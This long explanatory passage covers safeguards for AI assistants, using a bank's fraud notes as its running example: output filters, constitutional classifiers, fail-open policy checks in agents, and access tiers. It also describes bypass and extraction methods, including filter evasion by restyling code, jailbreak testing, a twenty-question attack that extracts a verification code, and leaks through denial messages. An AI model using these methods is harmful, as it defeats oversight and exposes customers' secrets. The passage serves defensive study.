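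In 2022, GitHub's coding assistant Copilot had an optional filter of this kind, which withheld a suggestion if about 150 characters matched code in its training data. Ippolito, Tramèr and colleagues (2022), in *Preventing Verbatim Memorization in Language Models Gives a False Sense of Privacy*, prompted Copilot for a well-known function from the video game Quake, and the filter correctly cut the function off. When they wrote the start of the function as a comment, or gave its variables French names, Copilot continued in the same style and the filter let the whole function through.

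They also built a stricter filter for other models. Before the model writes each token, code checks whether that token would complete a ten-token sequence on a list drawn from the training data. If so, the model must pick a different token. The list for an 800-gigabyte collection took up only 1.6 gigabytes because it left out rare sequences and was stored in a compact format, which occasionally causes the filter to block a harmless sequence.

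This filter blocks every listed sequence, but near copies got through. The models misspelled a word, changed the spacing or wrote "&" for "and", then continued the passage as before. In the worst case, counting near copies as well as exact ones doubled the number of memorised passages, although Ippolito and colleagues warn that their measure of near copies is imprecise.

Those models are several generations old, but newer ones probably make the problem worse. Copilot's output passed the filter because the model could recall the function and restyle it at the same time, and stronger models are better at both. Later research found a similar weakness in filters that classify text by its meaning, which can miss a harmful answer in altered wording if they aren't given the question.

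An overlap filter still helps the bank catch careless copying. It only has to compare each reply with the notes the assistant read in that conversation, so it can match runs as short as perhaps six words without blocking much else. If the note reads "card used at three petrol stations within an hour, suspect cloning", the filter will block a reply that quotes it but not one that says "we think somebody has copied your card".

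### Classifiers that score a reply as the model writes it

A classifier is a model trained to sort text into categories, so it has some chance of recognising a paraphrase. The most detailed public evidence comes from Anthropic, the company that makes Claude. Sharma, Tong and colleagues (2025), in *Constitutional Classifiers*, describe a system that keeps Claude from explaining how to make chemical, biological, radiological or nuclear weapons. Anthropic built it as follows:

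1. People write a "constitution", a plain-English list of forbidden and permitted kinds of content. Purifying restricted chemicals is forbidden, for example, and explaining high-school chemistry is permitted.
2. A language model writes many questions and answers of each kind.
3. Software produces variations on them by translating them, paraphrasing them and adding known jailbreak techniques.
4. Two classifiers learn from these examples and from a pool of harmless text. One reads the user's input, and the other reads the model's output.

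The output classifier doesn't wait for the whole reply. After each token *t*, it estimates the probability that the finished reply will be harmful, and it stops the reply as soon as

P(harmful | first *t* tokens) > θ,

where θ is a threshold that Anthropic sets. The user sees most replies without delay, but the system can't take back words it has already displayed. In one test, a programming error let through up to 128 more tokens after the classifier had raised an alarm, and a tester seemed at first to have beaten it.

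Anthropic tested two versions. It offered up to $15,000 for a universal jailbreak of the prototype, meaning one method that gets detailed answers to most forbidden questions in a field. About 183 active testers spent an estimated 3,000 hours or more on it. No jailbreak they reported got answers to all ten test questions with even half the detail of an unguarded model's answers. But the prototype refused about 44% of ordinary traffic on Claude's website, which made it impractical.

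The improved version was much less strict. It cut the success rate of automated jailbreak attempts about chemical weapons from 86% to under 5%. Refusals of ordinary traffic rose by 0.38 percentage points, or about 19 conversations in a sample of 5,000, with a larger rise for questions about chemistry. The classifiers added 23.7% to the computation needed to run the model. However, the human testers had attacked only the prototype, so the paper doesn't show that one system can both withstand them and refuse few ordinary requests.

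### The 2026 successor

The older output classifier read the reply without the question. "Yes, since Tuesday" looks harmless unless you know that Dana asked whether the fraud team was investigating her. *Constitutional Classifiers++* (Cunningham, Wei and colleagues, 2026) therefore uses an exchange classifier, which reads the question along with the reply so far.

That made the filter about 50% more expensive, so they added a cheaper first stage. In the final system, this is a probe, a simple weighted sum of the numbers that Claude computes internally as it writes. The numbers already exist, so the probe costs almost nothing to run. It averages its score over recent tokens, which keeps one odd word from setting it off. If the score is high enough, a separate classifier reads the exchange, and the system blocks the reply if the combined score

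0.55 × probe + 0.45 × classifier

passes a threshold. The probe sent about 5.5% of real traffic on to the classifier. Combining them also improved accuracy, because their mistakes overlapped less than those of two ordinary classifiers did.

The table compares four systems. A serious breach is an attack that obtained answers to more than five of eight forbidden questions, with at least half the detail of an unguarded model's answers.

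| System | Computing cost (older design = 100) | Serious breaches in human testing | Real traffic refused, % |
|---|---|---|---|
| Older design, rebuilt | 100 | 13 in 695,000 queries | 0.073 |
| Exchange classifier | 150 | 2 in 226,000 | 0.038 |
| Two classifiers in stages | 27.8 | 5 in 569,000 | 0.036 |
| Probe, then classifier | 3.5 | 1 in 198,000 | 0.050 |

The fall in cost is the clearest result. The new system costs 3.5% as much as the older classifiers, not 3.5% as much as Claude. If the older classifiers added about 24% to the cost of running the model, as in the 2025 paper, the new system would add less than 1%.

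The evidence for better protection is weaker. At the older design's rate, 198,000 queries would have produced 3.7 serious breaches on average, and one or none about 12% of the time, so the final system could have done this well by luck. The size of the improvement in refusals also depends on the baseline. Cunningham and colleagues compare their 0.05% with the 0.38% in the 2025 paper, but their rebuilt version of the older design refused only 0.073%.

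Testers have found universal jailbreaks for the older design and for both intermediate systems, though not for the final one.

Both papers come from Anthropic staff and deal with knowledge that is dangerous no matter who asks for it. The bank could write a similar constitution that forbids hinting that the fraud team suspects a customer but permits general advice about avoiding fraud. But "somebody used your card in Leeds" is a leak only if it comes from a note and Dana doesn't already know it. The classifier would have to read the note and the conversation as well as the reply, and neither paper tests that kind of judgement.

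### Why most alarms are false

A filter can be accurate and still be wrong in nearly all of its alarms if violations are rare. Suppose that 1 reply in 10,000 breaks the bank's rules. The filter detects 95% of these replies and wrongly flags 1% of the others. In a million replies, the results are:

| | Alarm | No alarm |
|---|---|---|
| Reply breaks a rule | 95 | 5 |
| Reply breaks no rule | 9,999 | 989,901 |

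There are 10,094 alarms, and only 95 of them, or about 0.9%, are right. In general, if a share π of replies breaks the rules, the filter detects a share *d* of those and wrongly flags a share *f* of the rest, the proportion of correct alarms is

πd / (πd + (1 − π)f).

Catching more violations would barely raise the share of alarms that are correct. Even if the filter caught every violation, only 1% of its alarms would be correct. Reducing false alarms helps much more. If the filter wrongly flagged 0.05% of harmless replies, about 16% of its alarms would be correct.

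The share of alarms that are correct also depends on who is using the assistant. If one account is attacking the assistant and a tenth of the replies to that account break a rule, about 91% of the original filter's alarms on that account are correct. An account that repeatedly sets off the filter therefore deserves much more attention than a single alarm.

### Blocking, referring or falling back

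If the bank blocks every flagged reply, it stops 95 leaks and spoils 9,999 good replies. This is worthwhile only if a leak harms the bank more than about 105 times as much as a spoiled reply does. That may well be true of a leaked fraud note, which could warn a thief, and is surely true of instructions for making a weapon, but it is much less likely for a minor internal policy. Many customers would also be affected. If false alarms are independent, a customer whose questions lead to 30 harmless replies has a 26% chance of having at least one blocked.

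Having a person review each alarm keeps good replies from being blocked but delays them. At one minute each, the 10,094 alarms would take about 168 hours to review, and only one in every 106 would be a real leak. At that rate, reviewers would very likely develop approval fatigue.

A second filter can reduce the reviewer's workload. Suppose it confirms 90% of the real leaks that the first filter flagged and only 5% of the false alarms. The reviewer would then have about 585 cases, of which about 86 would be real, but another nine or ten leaks would get through. This calculation assumes that the two filters make unrelated mistakes, although they may misclassify the same wording.

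The bank can also fall back to another model. When the filter flags a reply, the application discards it and gives Dana's question to a model that has never had the fraud notes in its context. The new reply can't contain the notes, and Dana still gets an answer if the alarm was false. By contrast, the output reviewer that Millstone and colleagues tested sometimes replaced useful answers with refusals. The fallback only works if the second model has seen neither the protected information nor the flagged reply.

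Anthropic uses fallback for some of its most capable models. Anthropic's *Claude Fable 5 and Claude Mythos 5* says that the company tuned Fable 5's safeguards conservatively and that they triggered in under 5% of sessions on average. That would be a lot of refusals for a popular product, but fallback lets most of those users get an answer from a less capable model.

### One model with two sets of safeguards

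A defender and a thief might type the same request for a working exploit, a program that takes advantage of a security flaw, so no filter can tell from the text alone which of them sent it. The company can instead decide in advance which accounts may receive the answer.

Anthropic has done this with Fable 5.1 and Mythos 5.1, which it released in September 2026. According to Anthropic's *System Card* (2026), they are the same model with identical weights, the numbers a model learns in training. Anyone can use Fable 5.1, which has extra safeguards for biology and cybersecurity. Mythos 5.1 relaxes some of those safeguards for people and organisations that Anthropic has vetted. In simplified form, the arrangement works like this:

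```
answer(request, account):
    unlocked = fields opened for this account   # set by vetting
    reply    = model(request)                   # may itself be a refusal
    if classifier flags the exchange in field f
       and f is not in unlocked:
        return fallback_model(request)
    return reply
```

The restriction covers an ability shown in testing. With its safeguards off, Mythos 5.1 wrote full working exploits in 245 of 250 trials on flaws in an old version of Firefox. Fable 5.1's classifiers consistently flagged tests of this kind and passed the requests to the older Claude Opus 4.8. Anthropic therefore considers Fable 5.1 no more useful for cyberattacks than Opus 4.8.

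OpenAI restricts the cyber capabilities of GPT-6 Astra in a similar way. OpenAI's *Safety overview* (2026) calls Astra the company's first model at the Critical level of cyber capability, where a model can find and exploit unknown flaws in many well-protected systems without step-by-step guidance. Campus Technology's *OpenAI's Astra Model Reaches Critical Cyber Threshold* (2026) reports that the general release can review code for security and write patches but refuses to create proof-of-concept exploits.

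According to *Path to Astra* (2026), OpenAI gives advanced cyber access first to a small group of alpha testers, then to members of a programme called Daybreak Blue. A spokesperson told Fortune (2026) that the testers include the US government and organisations that protect critical infrastructure, but OpenAI wouldn't name the organisations. OpenAI's *Expanding Daybreak as the Cyber Defense Window Narrows* describes Daybreak Blue as access to general-purpose models, with safeguards adapted to authorised defensive work.

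A user who gets no answer may not be able to tell which layer was responsible, but the companies' documents describe three:

| Layer | Claude Fable 5.1 and Mythos 5.1 | GPT-6 Astra |
|---|---|---|
| What the model refuses | Avoided helping with 94.7% of harmful requests with no system prompt, and 99.5% with the one on Claude's website | Refused 91.5% of requests in tests of cyber jailbreaks, compared with 59% for GPT-5.6 Sol |
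| What a classifier blocks | On Fable 5.1, offensive cyber work and some work that could be offensive or defensive | Suspected cyber misuse, partly by reading the model's internal activity |
| What the account unlocks | Biology for vetted users, with cyber access due to follow | Advanced cyber work for alpha testers, then for Daybreak Blue |

The two companies' refusal rates aren't comparable because Anthropic's cover sixteen kinds of harm, mostly outside cybersecurity, while OpenAI's come from attempts to break the cyber rules. Anthropic measured its rates without the classifiers, so they show how the model behaves on its own.

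The layers aren't always clearly separate. For accounts that OpenAI considers high-risk, the model itself refuses a wider range of cyber requests, and the monitoring system takes more context into account. Anthropic's classifiers also allow some cyber work for everyone. Fable 5.1 will look for flaws in source code, which defenders usually have, but not in compiled programs, which attackers often have to work from.

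An account permission is a trusted fact. This matters because Anthropic found that Mythos 5.1 accepts claims of authorisation that it can't verify somewhat more readily than Claude Opus 5 does. At the bank, the login system can turn off the fraud-note filter for members of the fraud team and keep it on for Dana.

However, the permission only decides which safeguards apply. The dangerous knowledge is in Fable 5.1's weights, so Anthropic can't withhold it from the public version the way the bank can withhold a fraud note. A member of the public who gets past both the model's refusal and the classifier can use the same abilities as vetted users. Anthropic describes this as extremely difficult but not impossible.

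A thief who steals a vetted account gets its permissions, and nothing in the software prevents a vetted user from passing an answer on. Anthropic also offers narrower access through Claude Security, which uses Mythos 5.1 to scan business customers' code for flaws and suggest patches for people to review, without giving those customers direct access to the model.

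## How enforcement outside the model fails

Nobody can get past the bank's gates, labels and filters by persuasion, but people wrote and configured them, and they can still fail. A bug can stop a check from applying, or a check can break and let everything through. A request can take a route that has no check, or the rule itself can be wrong. Even when every check works, an attacker can sometimes deduce a secret from answers the rules permit.

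### Copilot and the emails labelled confidential

Microsoft 365 lets a company attach labels such as "Confidential" to emails and documents. An administrator can then write a rule that keeps anything with that label away from Copilot. This is a form of withholding, since the text should never reach the model.

In early 2026 the rule stopped working for two mail folders, Sent Items and Drafts. Microsoft said in an advisory that labelled emails were "being incorrectly processed" by Copilot Chat, according to TechRadar's *Microsoft admits an Office bug exposed confidential user emails to Copilot* (2026). Office365ITPros' *Code Error Allowed Copilot Chat to Expose Confidential Information* (2026) reports that Microsoft attributed this to a "code issue" that let Copilot pick up items in those folders despite their labels. Other folders did not appear affected.

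The Stack's *28 days later copilot is probably not ingesting confidential email anymore* draws on a log of Microsoft's alerts to customers:

- **3 February:** Microsoft issued its first alert and began to deploy a patch within three hours.
- **10 February:** It marked the problem as ongoing since 21 January.
- **18 February:** It was contacting some of the affected users.
- **19 February:** It expected to complete the repair by its next update, which was due on 24 February.

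Office365ITPros gives 21 January as the date of the first customer reports. The Stack says it is unclear whether the date marks those reports or the update that broke the rule. Either way, the fault lasted nearly two weeks before the first alert. TechInformed (2026) reports that the fix had reached most affected systems by 20 February. It also reports that Microsoft's incident notices don't disclose when the defect was introduced, how many organisations it affected or how many emails Copilot processed.

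In ITPro's *Microsoft Copilot bug saw AI snoop on confidential emails*, a Microsoft spokesperson said the fault gave nobody access to information they weren't already authorised to see. The spokesperson said Microsoft's access controls and data protection policies "remained intact", but that Copilot had not behaved as Microsoft intended.

The first claim is plausible because the user had written the emails. But the rule barred Copilot from processing those emails for anyone. A company might want such a rule because text in Copilot's context can leak in other ways, as EchoLeak showed. There is no public evidence that this happened here, but Microsoft didn't answer when The Stack asked whether any of the content had leaked.

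Ordinary testing could have found the fault. As Office365ITPros points out, confidential messages routinely end up in Sent Items, so that folder is easy to check. A bank with a similar rule could keep a labelled test message in every folder and have a program ask the assistant about each one daily.

A more thorough method is to plant bugs in the gate and check whether the tests catch them. Millstone and colleagues did this with their proxy, and their tests caught all 23 of the planted bugs that changed its behaviour. But the tests didn't cover the part of the imitation back end that had a query bug. When the proxy added the owner's conditions to an agent's query, the back end sometimes couldn't interpret the result and fell back on a simpler reading. In 65 of the 116 affected trials, this made the query broader than the rules were meant to allow.

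### Checks that allow the call when they break

The proxy was designed to deny any query whose conditions it couldn't combine reliably, but the back end guessed instead, so the check failed open. Weng, Wang and colleagues (2026), in *When Code Becomes an LLM Call*, found the same behavior in many popular agents.

One example is Gemini CLI, Google's coding agent for the terminal. It has an optional policy enforcer that asks a language model whether a proposed tool call complies with a security policy. The model should answer allow, deny or ask the user. In simplified form, the code works like this:

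```
check(call):
    policy = the tool's policy, or an empty one if it has none
    reply  = model(policy, call)
    if the request to the model failed:   return ALLOW
    if the reply is empty:                return ALLOW
    if the reply cannot be parsed:        return ALLOW
    return the decision in the reply
```

The real function has six return paths, and five of them allow the call. It can deny a call only if the checking model returns a well-formed reply, so an outage at the model's provider would disable the enforcer without anyone noticing. An attacker might do the same by writing a tool argument that makes the checking model answer in the wrong format.

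Two other guards in Gemini CLI fail closed when a checker reports an error. But the enforcer turns each error into an ordinary ALLOW before it reaches them, so neither ever acts.

STORM, a program that writes encyclopedia-style articles, asks a model whether a topic is appropriate and tells it to answer exactly "Yes." or "No." The code rejects the topic only if the reply begins with "No", so it wrongly approves the topic when the model replies with a lowercase "no" or a refusal such as "I can't help with that".

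Weng and colleagues looked for such faults in 40 open-source agents, at 496 places where the program calls a language model and acts on the reply. For each place, one model listed the requirements from a description of the task, without seeing the code. Another listed the checks in the code, without seeing the requirements. A third compared the two lists. Human reviewers checked each stage, either in full or by sampling.

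The program ran checks both before and after the call at 82% of the places, but only 5.3% met all their requirements, and 63% of the individual requirements were unmet. Failing open accounted for 146 of the 1,697 gaps and appeared in 30 of the 40 agents.

Most of these gaps are harmless. Weng and colleagues set aside 83% of them because, for instance, a later check stopped the bad value or the only effect was a failed run. They also excluded faults that need a non-default setting, which would probably rule out the Gemini CLI enforcer. They traced the gaps that mattered to 60 faults and triggered 38 of them in practice. The table gives some of the results.

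| Program | Fault | Runs in which it occurred |
|---|---|---|
| JARVIS | Accepted a tool that was not among those on offer | 5 of 5 |
| GPT Researcher | Displayed report text as a web page without removing scripts | 5 of 5 |
| Skyvern | Ran a click that its own policy check had denied | 4 of 5 |
| CodeWhale | Ran any text that followed a certain marker as a program | 1 of 10 |
| OpenManus | Ran Python code that the model had written | 0 of 10 |
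| Khoj | Ran tools without an authorisation check | 0 of 10 |

Skyvern's policy check denied the click every time, but the code that performed the click never read the decision. In CodeWhale, the model refused to run the attacker's code and mentioned the marker while explaining why. The program then ran two fragments of that explanation as Python.

The zeros in the last two rows are weak evidence that those programs are safe. In OpenManus, the model recognised the attack all ten times. In Khoj, it refused or ignored the attack eight times and used the wrong format twice. Both programs still lacked the checks, and another model might have complied. Weng and colleagues replaced each program's usual model with DeepSeek-V4-Flash, so their figures show that a fault can occur but not how often it would for real users.

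Weng and colleagues wrote patches of 1 to 366 lines that stopped the original attack in all 38 cases. In 23 cases, the patch also stopped every variant they knew of. Many of the other 15 needed either a judgement about meaning, which simple pattern matching can't do, or a sandbox that the program didn't have.

### Routes without a check, and mistaken rules

GPT Researcher's developers had already added code to remove scripts in two of the places where the program displays text, but they missed the chat panel. Weng and colleagues found 101 gaps of this kind, where a check covers the main route but not the others.

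Until this year, Microsoft's rule for keeping labelled Office files from Copilot was designed to cover only files stored in certain places, so an administrator who assumed that the label worked everywhere would have been wrong. Microsoft's *DLP policies will be able to block Copilot processing of sensitivity‑labeled files* (2026) announced that the rule would cover Word, Excel and PowerPoint files wherever they are stored. Microsoft (2026) later moved the expected end of the rollout from May to the end of June.

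The proxy that Millstone and colleagues released also leaves some routes open. It handles complete requests and responses, but not responses that arrive in pieces. The Model Context Protocol, the standard many agents use to reach their tools, also lets a tool server supply documents and ready-made prompts, which need their own checks. A bank that installs a gate should therefore first list every way text can enter or leave the model's context, then block any route the gate doesn't cover.

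A gate that covers every route can still enforce the wrong rule. Suppose the label on each fraud note lets the "support" group and the fraud team read it. The bank then hires an outside call centre and adds its staff to the support group so that they can see customers' addresses. The fraud notes can now leave the bank, which breaks R3, although nobody has changed the label or the gate.

Software can find some mistakes in a set of rules. An analysis tool for Cedar, a language for writing rules, can detect rules that contradict each other, rules that never take effect and sets of rules that deny everything. It can't detect that the bank never meant to include the call centre, because the rules are consistent either way. Millstone and colleagues leave that check to the data's owner, and recommend that each description of the data's fields also has a named owner who updates it together with the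 rules.

Khoj, a personal assistant, has an optional feature that fetches web pages, including pages on the private network where Khoj runs. Its developers warned that this feature should stay off unless Khoj has only one user, but once an administrator turns it on, it works for everybody. Weng and colleagues used an ordinary account to fetch an internal page through the chat, without needing to trick the model.

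### Secrets worked out from permitted answers

Across all their trials with the full proxy, Millstone and colleagues recorded four answers that contained a protected email address. The proxy had worked correctly in all four trials, and the address had never entered the agent's context. The agent built the address from the person's name and the company's address pattern, both of which it could see. In some cases it wrote out the address while explaining why it wouldn't disclose it.

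Four answers in 1,065 trials is a low rate, but the rate depends on how predictable the secret is. An agent can't deduce a random card number from a customer's name, but it could easily guess that Dana's account is under investigation if it can see three payments on hold and a note field missing from her record. To prevent this, the bank would have to hide the held payments too, and then the agent couldn't help Dana with them.

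In another trial, the agent used search results to learn about a field it couldn't read. The proxy masked email addresses in the records it returned, but the agent could still search by address, and the back end ran each search on the real values. The agent searched for addresses containing "@partner" and got two matches, then searched for "yara" and "singh" and got one each. The agent reported these counts, which revealed part of the masked information.

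The automatic scoring missed this leak because no exact protected value appeared in the answer, so the proxy's 0.2% failure rate doesn't include it. One of the two judge models marked the answer as disclosing a protected fact, while the other marked it as revealing only that such data existed.

### Twenty questions for a six-digit code

A patient attacker can extract a whole secret this way. Suppose a thief has signed in with Dana's stolen password and wants to change her contact email. The gate for R2 has sent a six-digit code to Dana's phone, which the thief doesn't have. The bank has given the assistant a tool that searches the confirmation records, masking the code but reporting how many records match a search.

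The thief gets the assistant to count the records for Dana's account with a code of 500,000 or more. The answer is 1 or 0, which rules out half of the million possible codes. If the code is 271828, the search begins like this:

| Question | Answer | Codes still possible |
|---|---|---|
| 500,000 or more? | No | 500,000 |
| 250,000 or more? | Yes | 250,000 |
| 375,000 or more? | No | 125,000 |
| 312,500 or more? | No | 62,500 |

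Each yes/no answer halves the number of codes that remain possible, so twenty answers are enough to identify one code in a million (2²⁰ = 1,048,576). An agent could easily ask twenty questions before the code expires. The thief then enters the right code on the first attempt, so a limit on wrong codes doesn't help, and the gate for R2 allows the change.

Millstone and colleagues suggest three defences against leaks of this kind, but tested none of them.

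The gate can set a **query budget**, which limits how many questions anyone may ask about a protected field. After ten answers, the thief would still have up to 977 codes to choose from, and three guesses would succeed about 0.3% of the time. Without a limit, the thief would be certain to succeed, but 0.3% is still about a thousand times the chance of guessing the code with no answers at all. The gate also has to count questions across conversations, or the thief can get more answers by starting a new one. The budget will also block honest analysts who need many queries.

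**Minimum group sizes.** The tool can refuse to report a count below, say, 50. This stops the search for Dana's code, which concerns a single record. But an attacker can compare the counts for two large groups. If 212 customers in Leeds have a fraud flag, and 211 do when the search excludes Dana, then Dana has a flag. Millstone and colleagues compare the leak in their experiment to the "tracker", an attack on statistical databases that Denning, Denning and Schwartz described in 1979. The minimum also blocks legitimate questions about small groups, and a support assistant nearly always works with a single record.

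The tool can round each count to the nearest ten, so that 212 and 211 both become 210. An attacker can defeat this by adding other customers to both groups until the totals fall on either side of a rounding boundary, such as 215 and 214, which the tool would report as 220 and 210. Rounding also hides real differences from the bank's own analysts.

It is simpler to stop the assistant from searching by a field it may not read. However, the gate can't ban all searches on hidden fields, because the owner's rules may rely on them. For example, a rule may drop records marked "restricted". The gate has to distinguish the conditions the rules add from those the assistant writes, and reject only the assistant's conditions on hidden fields. At the bank, the assistant doesn't need the confirmation records, so the bank can withhold that tool instead.

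### What a denial reveals

A gate can leak information by denying a request. *Causality Laundering*, a preprint from April 2026, gives the example of an agent that reads an instruction to steal a computer's password file. The gate denies the request with "permission denied". A missing file would have produced "file not found", so the denial reveals that the file exists, and the agent can email that fact to the attacker. The email contains nothing from the file, so a label on the file's contents wouldn't stop it.

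An attacker can try a long list of files and use the pattern of denials to map what a system protects, though a single denial reveals little. *Causality Laundering* describes an agent that first passes the result through a harmless tool, such as a calculator, so the outgoing message contains only a number.

Its proposed remedy is to record denied calls as well as successful ones. When the gate denies a call, it links the denial to the agent's next call, as though information had passed between them. The rules can then block that next call if it would send something out. The link is a precaution, because software can't observe whether the denial influenced the model. An agent that triggers a denial by mistake and then tries to send a routine email may have that email blocked too. An attacker, however, might avoid the link by inserting an unrelated call between the denial and the email.

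The system was tested against just three attacks, only one of which relied on a denial. It blocked all three, and a simpler form of tracking missed all three.

A bank can remove much of the signal by giving the same reply whether a record is forbidden or doesn't exist. Copilot apparently doesn't do this. After Microsoft repaired the labelling fault, Office365ITPros tested the rule with a confidential email about an invented "Project Bunny". Copilot replied that it had found an internal reference but couldn't disclose the content. This obeyed the rule, but the same reply from somebody else's assistant would confirm that a secret project existed.

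Uniform replies can also mislead the agent. If the gate silently removes records, the agent may treat what remains as complete and tell a customer that she has no pending payments when she has three. If the gate warns the agent that something is missing, the warning reveals that protected data exists.

### What a monitor of a single run can't enforce

There is a theoretical reason these leaks are hard to stop. A gate can be modeled as a monitor that watches one run of a program step by step and can intervene only by stopping it. In *Enforceable Security Policies* (2000), the computer scientist Fred Schneider worked out which rules such a monitor can enforce.

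A monitor outside the model can enforce the rule "never send account details before the customer is verified". A run can break this rule only at a step where the program sends the details. The monitor has observed every earlier step, so it can check whether the customer has been verified and, if not, stop the run before the program sends them.

A monitor outside the model can't enforce the rule "the reply does not depend on whether Dana is under investigation". Suppose the assistant tells Dana that her payment will take two days. If it would have told her the same thing without an investigation, the reply reveals nothing. If it would have said "one hour" instead, the reply reveals the investigation. The monitor can't distinguish these cases because it checks only the steps of the actual run, which are identical in both.

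Clarkson and Schneider later named rules of this second kind hyperproperties, in their 2010 paper "Hyperproperties". An ordinary rule can be checked against each run separately, while a hyperproperty applies to a set of runs taken together. One example is noninterference, the requirement that public output must not depend on a secret. Showing that a system violates it requires at least two runs whose inputs differ only in the secret but whose public outputs differ.

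Labels get around the limit by enforcing a stricter rule that does concern a single run, which is that nothing can be sent to Dana once the fraud note has entered the context. Schneider gives a very similar example of an enforceable rule, which forbids a program to send messages after it has read a file. The stricter rule over-blocks because it also stops replies that the note didn't influence.

Labels also fail when they don't record everything that influenced a result. In the row-count leak, the search results contained no email addresses, so a label based only on the returned fields would have let the results through. To catch the leak, the label on a count must also cover every field that the search tested. Labels can miss the influence of denials in the same way, so *Causality Laundering* adds denials to the record.

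Withholding the note can satisfy the requirement itself, at least for the model's replies. If the note never reaches the model and nothing else in the model's input depends on it, that input is the same whether or not the note exists. The second condition is harder to meet because an investigation often has visible effects, such as a frozen card.

The bank can look for violations by comparing runs in a test system. It sets up two copies of an invented customer, identical except that one has a fraud note, and asks the assistant the same questions about each. A model's wording varies from run to run, so the bank has to repeat each question many times and look for consistent differences. A consistent difference is a leak, but if the bank finds none, other questions could still expose a leak.

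### When two barriers fail together

Since any single barrier can fail, engineers often put several in a row. Suppose the bank has two, and each misses 1% of attacks. It is tempting to multiply the rates and conclude that one attack in 10,000 gets through. But the correct calculation is

P(both miss) = P(first misses) × P(second misses, given that the first missed).

Two barriers that each miss 1% of attacks will together miss one in 10,000 only if they fail independently. If the second barrier misses 20% of the attacks that get past the first, the share that gets past both is 0.01 × 0.2 = 0.002, or one in 500, which is twenty times as many.

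Testing each barrier separately wouldn't reveal the difference. The table shows what could happen in 10,000 attacks.

| | Missed by the first only | Missed by the second only | Missed by both |
|---|---|---|---|
| Independent failures | 99 | 99 | 1 |
| Overlapping failures | 80 | 80 | 20 |

In both rows, each barrier misses 100 attacks, or 1%. To find out which row describes its system, the bank has to collect attacks that got past the first barrier and try them on the second.

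Two barriers that share a weakness are likely to miss the same things. Two language models that filter text may both miss the same unusual phrasing. Two gates that consult the same login system will both accept a thief who has signed in as Dana. In Gemini CLI, the enforcer hid its errors from the two guards behind it, so they could not catch anything those errors let through.

The bank could easily make a similar mistake with R3. Its first barrier is code that removes fraud notes from each record before the assistant reads it. Its second is the filter that compares each reply with the notes the assistant has read. Suppose the filter gets its list of those notes from the removal code. If a bug lets a note through but the code reports that it removed everything, the filter's list will be empty, and it will approve a reply that quotes the note word for word. The filter should instead fetch the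 notes for Dana's account directly from the fraud team's database, and block the reply if the database is unavailable.
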